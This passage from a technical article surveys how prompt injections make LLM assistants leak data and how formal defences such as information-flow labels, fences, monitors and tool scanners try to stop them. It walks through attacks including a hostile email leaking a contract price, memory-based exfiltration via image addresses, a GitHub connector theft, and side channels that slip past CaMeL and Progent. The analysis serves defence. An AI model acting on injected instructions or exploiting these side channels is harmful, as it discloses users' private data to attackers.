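Settings and order increase the number of combinations to check. If each of the 20 features has two settings, such as read-only and read-write, there are 760 pairs and 9,120 triples. Even without counting settings, if the order in which an attacker uses three features matters, each of the 1,140 triples becomes six sequences, for 6,840 in all.

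These numbers are a problem only for people who have to discover the rules by testing. A vendor that knew every rule could compute a single closure with all the features on. If that closure is safe, every smaller selection of features is safe too, because switching features off cannot add anything to the closure. Testers who don't know the rules can sample combinations instead of trying them all, but the sample can miss an unsafe one.

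If the full set of features is unsafe, the vendor needs to know which smaller sets make it unsafe. Spera calls an unsafe set minimal if removing any one member makes it safe. {Files, preview, popups} is minimal, so switching off any one of the three would prevent the theft. The paper claims that deciding whether a given set is minimal is coNP-complete, which would mean that there is probably no fast general method. But one closure calculation shows whether the set is unsafe, and one more for each member shows whether removing it makes the set safe, so a set of ten takes eleven quick calculations. The claim therefore can't be right unless every problem in coNP can be solved quickly, which is believed to be false.

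Listing every minimal unsafe set can take much longer, because there may be so many. If a theft needs ten steps and each step can use either of its own two features, the 20 features form 2¹⁰, or 1,024, minimal unsafe sets.

### Lampson's confinement problem

Computer scientists were asking how to keep a program from leaking data decades before LLM assistants existed. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who gives private data to a service, a program that belongs to someone else. The confinement problem is to run the service so that it can pass the data to nobody but the customer. Lampson assumes the service could be any program, including one written to leak, and the same assumption is appropriate for an assistant that is following an attacker's instructions.

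Some of Lampson's leaks are obvious, such as writing the data to a file that the service's owner can read later. Others use things people don't usually think of as communication. The service can encode data in the bill for its work, or vary how heavily it uses the computer so that another program can detect the changes in speed. Lampson called this last method a covert channel.

One leak in the list uses two features that are harmless on their own. Suppose a service may read a certain file but not write to it, and the operating system blocks writes to a file while another program is reading it. The service opens the file to signal a one and closes it to signal a zero. The owner's program tries to open the same file for writing, and learns the bit from whether the system refuses. Reading transmits nothing by itself, and the lock exists to prevent corrupted files.

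Lampson's argument applies to a product with a fixed set of features, because it does not depend on the system growing. The number of channels is "surprisingly large, but certainly not infinite", and a designer has to list them all and block each one. But Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in a system of even moderate complexity. A product with twenty features may have more than twenty channels, since one feature may leak in several ways.

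Lampson also required a confined program to remember nothing from one use to the next. Otherwise it could collect data and pass it to its owner the next time the owner called it. ChatGPT's memory stays on in Lockdown Mode, so an injection might be able to save a secret to memory in a protected chat and send it out later from a chat where the user has turned the mode off. A tester who examined only the protected chat would see no data leave.

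### When nobody can decide whether a right will leak

Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in Operating Systems*, asked whether a user could ever acquire a right they should not have, such as permission to read a file. They modeled the system as a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each file. Each cell lists the rights that user or program has over that file. A command checks whether certain rights are present and, if so, adds or removes rights, or creates or destroys rows and columns. A right leaks if some sequence of commands can put it in a cell that did not have it.

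They proved that no algorithm can answer this question for every such system. Their proof builds a protection system that simulates a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer. A chain of newly created rows serves as the machine's tape, the rights in the table record the symbols on it, and each command carries out one of the machine's moves. A chosen right leaks exactly when the machine reaches its final state. An algorithm that could predict leaks in every such system could therefore predict whether any Turing machine reaches its final state, which no algorithm can do.

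The construction needs an unlimited supply of new rows because the tape has no end, and a product with a fixed list of features and accounts can't provide them. Harrison and colleagues proved that if no command can create anything, an algorithm can always decide the question, although it would probably need exponential time in the worst case. They also stressed that safety may still be provable for particular systems. The textbook chapter *Foundational Results* gives an example from the same year, a system by Jones, Lipton and Snyder for which the question can be decided in time proportional to the system's size.

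Harrison and colleagues also covered a simpler case, in which each command makes a single change to the table. Tripunitara and Li later found an error in the proof of how hard that case is to decide (*The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*).

The 1976 theorem therefore does not imply that Lockdown Mode is impossible to verify. Spera's closure avoids the difficulty because its list of capabilities is finite and its rules add capabilities from that list without removing any. A product comes closer to the theorem's general case when the assistant can create new agents, shared links or accounts, each with its own rights.

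A guarantee about rights would also fall short of what Alice needs, because Victor obtained the contract price without gaining any new right.

### Secure parts, insecure whole

In Spera's example, the only thing proved about *a* and *b* is that each is harmless by itself. *Noninterference and the composability of security properties* (McCullough, 1988) considers parts that meet a much stricter standard, noninterference, which requires that nothing an observer sees depends on the secret data. For systems that behave partly at random, one version requires that an observer of public events can never rule out any sequence of secret inputs.

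*Romulus, a Computer Security Properties Modeling Environment* (Brackin, Foley, McCullough and colleagues, 1996) describes two machines that each meet this standard but leak when connected. Machine A receives secret messages and sends its own at unpredictable times. At some point it publicly announces "stop", and then whether the total number of secret messages received and sent so far was odd or even. An observer learns nothing about the messages A received, because A may have sent one more or one fewer of its own. Machine B works the same way, except that it stops counting when it receives A's "stop".

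When the machines are connected, each sends its own secret messages to the other. If four messages pass between them and no secret message arrives from outside, both machines count four and announce "even". If a secret message also arrives at A from outside, A counts five and announces "odd" while B still announces "even". An observer who sees the two machines disagree knows that a secret message came in, because each machine now counts the random messages that had hidden the other's secret inputs.

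Like Lampson's argument, this one applies to fixed products, since it needs only two small machines. It shows that some combinations of secure parts are insecure, but not how many are. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995) proved that connecting parts preserves noninterference when there is no feedback, meaning that nothing a part sends out can return to it through another part. They also gave a method of connecting parts that preserves noninterference when there is feedback. LLM agents have constant feedback, because the result of each tool call returns to the model and influences the next call.

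McCullough's remedy was a stronger requirement called restrictiveness, which still holds when parts that meet it are connected. A secret input must not change anything that affects a machine's public behaviour, so the machine reacts to the next public input as though the secret had never arrived. Machine B fails this requirement because a secret message just before "stop" changes what it announces.

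Spera's claim that better component design cannot fix the failure is too strong, because a strict enough check on each component, such as restrictiveness, can give a guarantee about the whole system, even though weaker checks cannot. Restrictiveness is hard for an assistant to satisfy. If a model reads a private file and then writes a web search, the search may depend on the file, so the model fails the requirement unless something else controls what it sends. Proofs about whole agents therefore tend to rely on software around the model.

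### Would one complete barrier be enough?

If no data can leave the system, we don't need to know which features could combine to steal it. In the model, suppose every rule that produces theft requires an outbound request, the system does not start with one, and no rule produces one. Theft can then never enter the closure, because the request it requires is never available. This holds for 20 features or 200, regardless of how many pairs and triples they form.

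In the extreme version, which Lampson called total isolation, a confined program makes no calls to any other program. He also called it impractical, but a looser form has an advantage over checking combinations of features. A barrier outside the features, such as a network with no route to the internet, covers new features by default, so nobody has to remember to add them to a list.

The weak point is the assumption that no rule produces an outbound request, since preview and popups produced one. If the barrier is complete, the combinations behind it don't matter, but the vendor still has to rule out combinations that let a request through. This is a smaller task than finding every possible theft, because it concerns a single outcome and doesn't require anyone to predict which data an attacker will want.

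Besides blocking web requests, a complete barrier has to enclose each customer's account separately, extend to the user's own device and cover domain name lookups, since Check Point found a way out at each of those three points. It also has to hold for as long as the secret stays in the system, including in memory that a later chat can use.

Lecture slides from Purdue University summarise a 1975 reply to Lampson by Steven Lipner, who concluded that designers could close storage and legitimate channels with little loss of efficiency, but that closing covert channels seemed to reduce performance unreasonably. To stop a program from signalling through its timing, for example, the system would have to show every other program a clock that the signalling program does not affect. Lipner doubted that this was possible, because users can also tell the time by other means. Lampson's less demanding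 alternative was to accept some leakage and limit how much a channel can carry. Like a cap on web requests, this limit does not protect very short secrets.

Enabled apps are different because the customer wants these openings. For legitimate channels, Lampson proposed a rule called masking, which lets the customer decide everything that goes out. Alice could follow it by writing the comment for ticket 212 herself before the assistant opened her mail or the wiki, so that the comment could not depend on the contract price. But masking rules out having the assistant read the material and write the comment, which is why most people use one.

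Knowing which few features can send data out saves reviewers a lot of work. If only two of 20 features can do so, every theft has to use at least one of them. Reviewers then need to check only the 37 of 190 pairs and 324 of 1,140 triples that include at least one of the two. They can skip the other 969 combinations, provided that the remaining 18 features cannot together create another way out.

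## How strong a guarantee can be proved for an LLM agent?

Researchers have proved that prompt injection cannot make certain LLM agents disclose more than their task already does, even if the LLM obeys the attacker. The proofs concern mathematical models of agents, and each depends on stated conditions. The theorem closest to Alice's problem does not cover the usual kind of assistant, whose LLM chooses every tool call as it goes.

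Some of these systems track where each piece of data came from and who may receive it. Others remove tools before the model can start following instructions from an untrusted source. Both approaches still allow some communication, unlike Lampson's total isolation.

### Labels on the data

Information-flow control means labelling data by origin and secrecy, and checking the labels before each action. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe a Microsoft system called FIDES that does this for LLM agents. Applied to ticket 212, where Victor's email made Alice's assistant post a confidential price, the method has three steps:

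1. The software labels each item as a tool returns it. The label records who may read the item and whether its source is trusted. The wiki page gets "staff, trusted", and Victor's email gets "Alice and Victor, untrusted".
2. The software carries the labels forward. Text made from two items may go only to people allowed to read both, and it is untrusted if either item is. Software can't tell which parts of a conversation influenced the model, so the model's output gets the combined label of everything in it. After the assistant has read both items, that label is "Alice only, untrusted".
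3. The software checks the label before it runs a tool call. All staff and Victor can see ticket 212, but only Alice may read this text, so the software refuses the comment.

Step 3 adds the check that Alice's apps lacked. The software allows the comment only if *V* ⊆ *R*, where *V* is the set of people who can see the comment and *R* is the set of people allowed to read its contents. FIDES can also require that every consequential action come from a trusted conversation. The comment fails that check too, because the conversation contains Victor's email.

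The same checks also block legitimate work. If Alice only wants to copy a new delivery date from Victor's email into the ticket, the date is still untrusted text that only Alice and Victor may read, so the software would not show it to her colleagues.

FIDES recovers some of this work by hiding untrusted text from the model that plans the task. The software stores the email in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name, so the conversation keeps its trusted label. The planning model can pass the variable to a tool, or have a separate model with no tools extract the date from it. An administrator could then let the wording of a comment depend on untrusted text, as long as the choice of ticket depends only on the trusted conversation. The administrator would also have to allow staff to see delivery dates from suppliers' emails.

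In some tasks, however, the planning model must learn something from the email before it can choose the next step. The software can restrict the isolated model's answer to yes or no, which limits the attacker's influence on the plan to one bit per answer.

Costa and colleagues prove that this kind of tracking can enforce explicit secrecy. This property requires any fixed sequence of tool calls to produce the same publicly visible results when run on two sets of data that differ only in their secrets. It does not cover what an observer can learn from which sequence the agent chose, which researchers call an implicit flow. For example, if the assistant comments on one ticket when the price is above $150,000 and on another when it is below, Victor can learn something about the price even if neither comment contains it. Explicit secrecy also does not cover leaks through timing or the size of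 network packets.

In tests on AgentDojo with the model GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent and none succeeded against FIDES with its checks on. However, Costa and colleagues assumed good labels in these tests. They marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it, whereas a company labelling its own mail and documents has no list of future attacks to work from.

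### Separating the plan from untrusted text

CaMeL, described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025), separates planning from reading more strictly. One model receives the user's request but no untrusted text, and writes a program to carry out the request. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and returns values to the program, but cannot call tools. An interpreter runs the program, records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks each tool call against a policy.

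Victor's email could make the quarantined model return the wrong delivery date, but it could not add a wiki search to the program, because the planning model had finished writing the program before any part of the system read the email.

Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and that no injection succeeded within its threat model. CaMeL used nearly three times as many tokens. Its developers demonstrated two side-channel attacks on it, one through an indirect dependency and one through an error that the attacker triggers.

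Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, describe further leaks. CaMeL blocks a program that directly emails the attacker if a private bank balance is above a threshold. It misses a roundabout version, based on an example from the 1970s. The program starts with two public variables, `tmp` and `rich`, both true:

1. If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false.
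2. If `tmp` is still true, the program sets `rich` to false.
3. If `rich` is still true, the program emails the attacker.

When the balance is high, the interpreter marks `tmp` as private in step 1. The program then skips the assignment in step 2, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as private. In step 3, the interpreter sees that `rich` is public and allows the email. When the balance is low, the program sends nothing. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is above the threshold, although no label check failed.

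An attacker would have trouble planting this program, because CaMeL's planning model does not read untrusted text. But a guarantee about the interpreter must hold for every program the interpreter accepts.

The other leak comes from ordinary code outside the interpreter, which restarts failed runs without tracking labels. Whether the policy blocked a run can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. At that rate, 27 attempts would be enough to reveal Alice's eight-digit account number.

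### Why noninterference is too strict

Noninterference would rule out all of these leaks. If Obs(*s*, *a*) is what the attacker sees when the secret is *s* and the attacker's input is *a*, it requires

Obs(*s*₁, *a*) = Obs(*s*₂, *a*) for every pair of secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂ and every input *a*.

An assistant meant to share some data cannot meet this requirement. Dongol gives the example of a calendar assistant that replies to meeting requests with its owner's free times. Calendars with different free times produce different replies, so the assistant fails even though it is doing what its owner asked. Costa and colleagues reject noninterference for a similar reason. Enforcing it would essentially forbid any tool call with a visible effect after the agent has used a tool that may read private data.

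The usual way to relax noninterference is declassification, in which someone writes a policy listing what the system may release. An assistant that handles many kinds of requests would need a policy for each task. Dongol proposes deriving the policy from the task.

### Comparing the agent with one that ignores injections

Dongol calls this alternative relative security. It applies to agents that plan which tools to use, and in what order, before they read any untrusted content. The reference agent runs the same plan under the same monitor, but its model never follows injected instructions.

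An agent leaks a pair of secrets if the attacker, using the same input in both cases, can tell one secret from the other. The agent is relatively secure if a reference agent leaks every pair that the first agent leaks. The attacker may need a different input to tell the two secrets apart with the reference agent.

Suppose an email tells the calendar assistant to send its owner's calendar. If the model obeys, the attacker learns when the owner is free. Relative security allows this because an honest meeting request would have revealed the same thing. If the email also asks for a password reset code, sending it violates relative security because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

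Dongol points out a weakness in this definition. Suppose an assistant is meant to answer yes or no when someone guesses a secret number, and an injection makes it send the whole number instead. An attacker could tell any two possible numbers apart by giving the reference agent a well-chosen guess, so the injection does not violate relative security. For Alice's account number, the definition would treat theft in a single message as equivalent to theft that might take 100 million guesses.

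A stricter version, uniform relative security, fixes the reference agent's input before anyone knows the secrets. One guess can then reveal only whether that guess was right, so the theft violates this version.

Removing a tool can also turn a relatively secure agent into an insecure one. If the planned task already sends a report to the attacker, an injection that sends the same report through a web request reveals nothing new. If the vendor then disables the planned message but leaves web requests on, the reference agent no longer reveals the report, so the injection becomes a leak. In Spera's model of combined features, by contrast, disabling a feature can never make a safe system unsafe. The results differ because relative security measures what the attack adds to the task, while Spera's model measures what the system can do.

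### The fence theorem

The monitor that protected Alice's account number by withdrawing the fetch tool is an example of a fence. Dongol proves that an agent is relatively secure if, when it first reads untrusted data, the fence permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call. The result holds for every plan and any text the model mistakes for an instruction.

The theorem has several conditions:

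- Each instruction the model obeys produces a single tool call.
- The model may obey at any time, but its timing must not depend on a secret or on the monitor's answers.
- The attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing.
- The run eventually ends. For an agent that runs indefinitely, the model must not go on obeying injections forever without returning to the plan.

The proof compares the two agents step by step. They behave identically until the model tries to make an injected call. By then the agent has read something untrusted, so the monitor has already withdrawn the tool and blocks the call. The attacker sees nothing, and the reference agent waits. The real agent then continues with the plan, and the attacker has seen the same things from both agents. The proof also establishes the stricter, uniform version of relative security. Isabelle, a program that verifies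 every logical step, checked the whole development of about 31,600 lines.

The result is even stronger for Alice's email summary because her plan sends nothing outside. The reference agent therefore reveals nothing, and the real agent satisfies noninterference for an attacker who cannot observe timing.

The fence has to be in place before the model sees any untrusted text. The late block described earlier is one of three positions that Dongol compares:

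| Order of events | What an injection can still send |
|---|---|
| Read the email, read the secret, stop sending | The secret |
| Read the email, stop sending, read the secret | Private data already in memory |
| Stop sending, read the email, read the secret | Nothing |

Private data can still leak in the middle order. The assistant can no longer send anything by the time it reads the secret, but assistants often start with private data from earlier work, and the model can send that data as soon as it has read the email.

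This differs from a related problem in processor design, from which Dongol takes the idea of relative security. Processors run some instructions early, based on a guess, and attacks such as Spectre exploit this to leak data. A barrier just before the leaking code can stop these attacks. In an LLM agent, the injection supplies the leaking call, and the model may make that call at any point after reading the injection, so it is not safe to place the barrier any later than that reading.

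Dongol also models the theft of data from private GitHub repositories, which Willison used as an example of one connector meeting all three conditions for an attack. A hostile issue makes the agent publish private data in a pull request. Withdrawing the pull-request tool when the agent reads the issue blocks the theft, but it would also stop the agent from proposing a fix for the issue, which may be what the user wanted. Relative security does not measure this loss, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and also loses the tool.

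### Approving a tool and approving an exact call

An approval lets the agent use a tool after reading untrusted content. Suppose Alice approves a draft reply to an email, but the monitor records only that the agent may send one message. The model follows an instruction in the email and sends her private data before the planned reply goes out. The monitor allows this message because Alice approved the tool, then refuses her actual reply because the approval has been used up.

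A limit on the number of messages has the same flaw, because it controls how many messages leave but not which ones. An injection can use up the allowance before legitimate messages are sent.

If the monitor instead records the exact arguments Alice approved, it refuses any message that differs from them. Dongol proves that this monitor is relatively secure for injected send calls if the attacker cannot observe timing and the model does not keep obeying injections forever.

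An attacker who can observe timing may still learn whether the private data matches the approved reply. Suppose the injection tries to send the private data just before the planned reply. If the two match, the monitor allows the injected message, and the attacker receives it one step early. If they differ, the reply arrives at its normal time.

The proof assumes the approved text is trusted, so it would not have protected the contract price. The comment on ticket 212 already contained the price when Alice approved it. Approving the exact call guarantees that ChatGPT posts what she approved, but not that she noticed what it contained.

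### What the fence theorem assumes and leaves out

Dongol lists seven assumptions that the deployed software must satisfy:

| Assumption | What it requires | How a product could break it |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted execution | Ordinary software runs the plan, and the model cannot skip or change a step | The model changes the recipient of a planned email |
| Complete mediation | Every tool call and every untrusted read passes through the monitor, which handles requests one by one | The agent uses a browser that the monitor does not control |
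| Mediated reads | Untrusted text reaches the model only after the monitor has allowed the read | The software loads an email before the fence takes effect |
| Silent denials | A refused request has no effect the attacker can see | The refusal appears in a public log |
| Limited observation | The attacker cannot see the monitor's state or the effects of the agent's internal steps | Displaying an answer loads an image from the attacker's server |
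| Fresh sessions | A new session clears everything the model has kept from untrusted content | Long-term memory carries an instruction into the next chat |
| Trusted channels | The attacker cannot write to sources the agent treats as trusted | A calendar accepts invitations from outsiders |

SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT that Rehberger published in 2024, violated the assumption about fresh sessions. A hostile page made ChatGPT save an instruction in its memory. In later chats, the instruction made ChatGPT display images whose addresses contained the user's messages. In Dongol's model of the attack, the fence disables image loading when the agent reads a web page but not when the agent loads its memory. The attack fails if the fence also treats memory as untrusted.

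The theorem also leaves out side channels, systems of several cooperating agents, and attacks that make an agent do something harmful without leaking data. It does not measure how much data leaks or how likely a leak is. Dongol also excludes mistakes in the plan, attacks that manipulate which tool the model selects, and tools whose reply depends on the request. One example of such a tool is a search engine run by the attacker, who could read private data in a query and then choose the results.

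The most important exclusion from Dongol's theorem is the standard agent design described at the outset, in which the model chooses every call. Such an agent has no fixed plan, so there is no reference agent to compare it with. Vendors can still put a fence around it, and the fence would block the same calls, but they cannot cite the theorem as proof that the agent is secure.

### A theorem that covers agents which write code

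Garby and colleagues developed LLMbda, a small programming language for building LLM agents. Every value in it, including the conversation with the model, carries a label. The interpreter updates the labels as the program runs and stops the program if a private condition is about to change a public conversation. CaMeL lacks this kind of check in its handling of `tmp` and `rich`.

Garby and colleagues prove a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including agents that generate and run code, so the theorem does not require a plan fixed in advance. It also makes no assumption about how the interpreter reads the model's replies, so a hostile reply cannot bypass it. The proof checker Lean verified the theorem.

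LLMs produce varying answers, so the theorem compares probabilities. Let *μ* and *ν* give the probability of each visible result for two different secrets. Each may add up to less than one, because a run may never finish, or the interpreter may stop it for breaking a policy. The theorem requires that some distribution *ω*, with a total of at most one, satisfy *μ* ≤ *ω* and *ν* ≤ *ω* for every result. It follows that

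distance between *μ* and *ν* ≤ (*d*₁ + *d*₂) ÷ 2,

where *d*₁ and *d*₂ are the probabilities that the two runs do not finish. The distance is half the sum of the differences between the probabilities of each result. If both runs always finish, the attacker sees exactly the same distribution for both secrets. If one fails to finish 10% of the time and the other 20%, the distributions can differ by at most 15 percentage points.

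A secret can therefore affect whether a run finishes. CaMeL's retry loop allowed an attacker to repeat this kind of leak. Garby and colleagues put their agent's retry loop inside the language, where the interpreter tracks it. The agent retries on artificial data until its program works, and only then runs the program on the real data.

The language also lets a program endorse untrusted data, relabelling it as trusted. A second theorem shows that an attacker cannot use endorsement to leak secrets, whatever untrusted input they choose. Endorsement does, though, weaken protection against untrusted data influencing an action. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs, both with GPT-5.2 in a version of the agent that could endorse data.

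Even with LLMbda, a program must relabel private data as public to send a private calendar to an outsider, and someone has to decide what the assistant may share. Garby and colleagues explain that their construction can support this relabeling, but the theorem would then protect trust labels and no longer guarantee secrecy.

### Data that persists between requests

An assistant with a memory needs to keep labels across tasks, not only within one. In *SPA*, Girrens and Wang (2026) describe a user who asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice, and on Tuesday to pay it. An attacker has put their own account number in the invoice, so the agent could pay the attacker even if it ignores every injected instruction and follows the user's request exactly.

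SPA plans each request once, before running any tool. It stores results with their labels and shows the planning model only a description of each result, such as "invoice details from Monday's request". When a plan uses a stored result, SPA restores the original label. An account number from an untrusted invoice on Monday is therefore still untrusted on Tuesday, and SPA rejects a plan that passes it to the payment tool if that tool requires trusted input.

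SPA checks the whole plan, including conditional actions, before executing any of it. If an untrusted email determines whether the agent makes a payment, SPA treats the payment as untrusted even if the amount and recipient came from the user. If a plan fails the check, SPA does not ask the model for another, because repeated attempts could help an attacker find one that passes.

Girrens and Wang adapted AgentDojo so that tasks extended over several requests. With label checks on, attacks succeeded in 0.2% of cases, and two of the runs counted as successes were ones where SPA had rejected the plan. The test provides little evidence about delayed attacks, because attacks succeeded only 0.6% of the time even when the researchers turned the label checks off and showed stored data directly to the planning model. Most of the injected instructions never affected a later request, so SPA had little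 to prevent.

### Testing an enforced policy

Proofs do not show whether people can write suitable policies or whether an agent remains useful under them. Narisetty and colleagues' June 2026 test of Progent, described earlier, gives some evidence on both. Average attack success fell from 25.8% to 4.2%, and was 2.6% under a tailored attack. Progent checks the name and arguments of each tool call but does not track where the arguments came from.

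The tailored attack targeted the language model that writes Progent's rules. It described the malicious action as a routine step that someone had already authorised, to get the model to add it to the permitted calls. Narisetty and colleagues suspect this milder wording also made the agent less likely to carry out the action. The low figure may therefore reflect a weak attack as well as a strong defence.

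The average also includes a set of office tasks in which no attack succeeded, even without Progent:

| Tasks | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, tailored attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack messaging | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Without the office tasks, the averages would be 38.7%, 6.4% and 4.0%. Progent clearly helped, but the test was small, with one model, one template for the tailored attack, eight user tasks in each set and three runs. The researchers did not try an attack that used only calls the rules already allowed, the obvious choice for an attacker who knew the rules.

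Enforcement was costly in all four of these systems:

| System | Test conditions | Tasks completed without enforcement | Tasks completed with enforcement | Source |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Four sets of tasks, GPT-4o | 84% | 50% | Costa and colleagues |
| CaMeL | Banking tasks, GPT-5.2 | 67% | 38% | Garby and colleagues |
| SPA | Four sets of tasks, GPT-5.4-nano | 53% | 29% | Girrens and Wang |
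| Progent | Three sets of tasks under attack, Qwen2.5-7B | 45% | 27% | Narisetty and colleagues |

The figures can't be used to rank the systems, because the models and tasks differ. FIDES and Progent were compared with an ordinary agent, while CaMeL and SPA were each compared with the same system with its policy checks turned off. The CaMeL result covers only 16 banking tasks and has wide margins of error, which may partly explain why the loss is much larger than the fall from 84% to 77% in its developers' own tests.

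Better models can recover some of the loss. FIDES completed 41% of travel tasks with GPT-4o and 68% with o1, a reasoning model that handled the hidden variables better. But some failures are intended. Several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the payment instructions in it, which a rule against acting on untrusted text forbids.

### How a product can fall outside the proof

A proof covers a model of the system. The product can differ from that model even if the proof is correct and the software enforces every rule in it.

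Wrong labels are one way this can happen. Suppose the software labels the ticket tracker "visible to staff" and nobody updates the label when the project lead invites Victor. The check *V* ⊆ *R* then passes, and the software posts the price where Victor can read it. Labels on incoming text can be wrong too. If Alice pastes a paragraph from a stranger's website into her request, most systems will treat it as her own words. According to Narisetty and colleagues, FIDES as deployed treats unlabeled data as trusted.

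The product may also have an outbound channel that the formal model omits. Dongol's theorem requires the fence to withdraw every tool an injection can call. An engineer might reasonably have left ChatGPT's code container available because it blocked direct internet connections, but it could still leak data through domain name lookups. In LLMbda, the code that contacts the LLM over the network is outside the verified interpreter. Its tests used simulated banking tools written in LLMbda itself, so the tests could not reveal side effects of a real bank's systems.

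A feature added after a product's release can make a proof's conditions false. For example, the web page preview that OpenAI added to ChatGPT gave injected text a new way to send requests. A fence designed before then would have kept withdrawing the tools on its list but left the preview available. The theorem holds for any set of tools, so a vendor would not need a new proof, but it would have to add the preview to the fence and recheck the seven assumptions, including whether anything the preview sends can bypass the monitor.

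## How can risky combinations be found before attackers find them?

Vendors and researchers look for risky combinations by analysing a system's tools and by attacking the system. Analysis can cover thousands of tools, but it misses any channel that nobody has described. An attack shows what works, but most organised tests set the attacker's entry point and goal in advance, so they rarely uncover a new way for data to leave the system.

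### Listing what each tool can do

An inventory lists every capability and records whether it can bring in untrusted text, read private data or act as a sink. The security company Snyk labels tools this way. In its example, the coding assistant Cursor could read tickets that anyone could submit, read files on the programmer's computer, and send web requests. Snyk's scanner, Agent Scan, lists the AI agents, tool servers and skills installed on a computer.

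Part of an inventory for Alice's assistant might look like this:

| Capability | Brings in untrusted text? | Reads private data? | Sink? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading mail | Yes | Yes | Not for outsiders |
| Searching the wiki | No | Yes | Not for outsiders |
| Commenting on tickets | No | No | Yes, if a guest can read the ticket |
| Running code in a container | Yes, from uploaded files | Yes, from uploaded files | Yes, through domain name lookups |
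| Previewing a web page | Yes, if the page is hostile | Yes, if the page contains private text | Yes, through popups |

An engineer working from OpenAI's descriptions would probably have written "no" in the sink column for the container and the preview. Check Point Research found the container's hidden channel by testing it. The reliability of an inventory therefore depends on how well each "no" in that column has been tested.

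Even listing the tools can be hard. Many assistants use tools offered by programs called MCP servers, which follow the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in late 2024. *Unsafe by Flow* (Hou, Zhao and Wang, 2026) examined 100 MCP projects in Python and 100 in JavaScript or TypeScript. Of these, 32 Python projects and 12 JavaScript or TypeScript projects did not fit any of three common patterns for declaring tools, so a scanner that knows only those patterns could miss their tools.

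A scanner's results can depend heavily on how it inspects a server. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (2026) tested a scanner on nine deliberately vulnerable servers. When it only read the code, the scanner flagged both Python servers but none of the seven JavaScript ones, because it could not parse them properly. It flagged all seven when it ran them in a sandbox and monitored their behavior.

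### Searching a set of tools for attack paths

Toxic flow analysis searches an inventory of tools for sequences that could leak data. Invariant Labs (2025), Snyk's research division, introduced the method after demonstrating an attack through the GitHub connector. The attack made an agent publish a user's salary and plans to move abroad, although Invariant Labs had not tampered with any of the tools.

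Toxic flow analysis starts with a graph of the order in which an agent could use its tools. Each tool carries labels for how far to trust its output, how sensitive its data is and whether it can act as a sink. The software then looks for dangerous sequences and scores them. Invariant Labs published no accuracy figures with its preview. Thoughtworks' *Toxic flow analysis for AI* (2026) calls the method a primary technique for examining agents but rates it "Assess", the consultancy's label for methods worth exploring.

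Zha, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Smith in Action*, measured a similar method. Their scanner, SCAN-MCP, analyses the tools of one MCP server at a time:

1. It finds the code behind each tool.
2. An LLM identifies the sources and sinks in that code.
3. For every ordered pair of tools, the LLM judges whether the first could produce something the second uses, such as a file, or make the second possible.
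4. Ordinary software joins these pairs into chains of up to four tools. It keeps chains that start with untrusted input and end in an operation that could do damage or send data out.
5. The LLM writes an attack for each remaining candidate and states what effect it should have.

The researchers ran SCAN-MCP and four other scanners on the same 100 servers, then tried to reproduce each report by hand in an isolated environment:

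| Scanner | Reports | Confirmed | Share not confirmed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SCAN-MCP | 150 | 124 | 17% |
| An LLM given the raw code | 126 | 64 | 49% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 191 | 70 | 63% |
| Semgrep | 141 | 27 | 81% |
| mcp-scanner | 2 | 0 | 100% |

Some unconfirmed reports may describe real flaws that the researchers couldn't test because they lacked the necessary logins or storage services. SCAN-MCP did especially well on chains of tools, where the researchers confirmed 19 of its 20 reports. The LLM alone found six of those chains, and the other three scanners found none. In all 19 cases, the attack failed when the researchers used only the last tool in the chain, so testing that tool by itself would have missed the problem.

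One chain involved a server that lets an agent control a browser. The agent opens the attacker's website, clicks the site's file-selection button and uploads a private file from the user's computer. The server's developers first told Zha and colleagues that the report was out of scope, but about two weeks later they changed how the server handled uploads, which fixed the problem.

Across 10,121 public servers, SCAN-MCP produced 27,123 reports, of which 8,422 described chains. These totals include attacks that run commands or alter files as well as data theft. We can't infer from them how many chains are real, because none of the 20 chain reports that the researchers checked came from servers with at least 50 tools, which accounted for 31% of all chain reports.

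SCAN-MCP's filters helped keep its false-alarm rate low, but they also discarded real flaws. With the filters off, it produced 519 reports, of which the researchers confirmed 168. The filters had removed 44 real findings, including eight chains. A vendor checking one product would have time to investigate the extra reports, but a marketplace with thousands of servers probably would not.

SCAN-MCP also doesn't analyse chains that cross between servers. If Alice's mail, wiki and ticket tracker each had its own server, it would miss Victor's theft of the contract price. A vendor that connects apps from many suppliers needs to analyse the apps together, because no single supplier can see the whole path.

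MCP-BiFlow, a scanner by Hou and colleagues, traces data from requests into sensitive operations. It also traces outside content as it flows to the model, which is how an injection arrives. It detected 30 of 32 known vulnerabilities. In 15,452 public repositories, it flagged 549 groups of suspicious results, and manual review confirmed 118 vulnerable paths in 87 servers.

*VIPER-MCP* (2026) reports that its scanner raised no false alarms on servers without known flaws. The scanner confirms suspected flaws by attacking the running server, but it missed types of flaw it had no model for, such as SQL injection. Its result is not directly comparable with SCAN-MCP's 17%, which is the share of reports that the researchers could not confirm. Even a scanner that wrongly flags few sound servers can produce a high share of wrong reports. For example, if 100 of 10,000 servers are vulnerable and a scanner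 catches them all but wrongly flags 1% of the others, it raises 99 false alarms, so about half its reports are wrong.

### Training a model to attack

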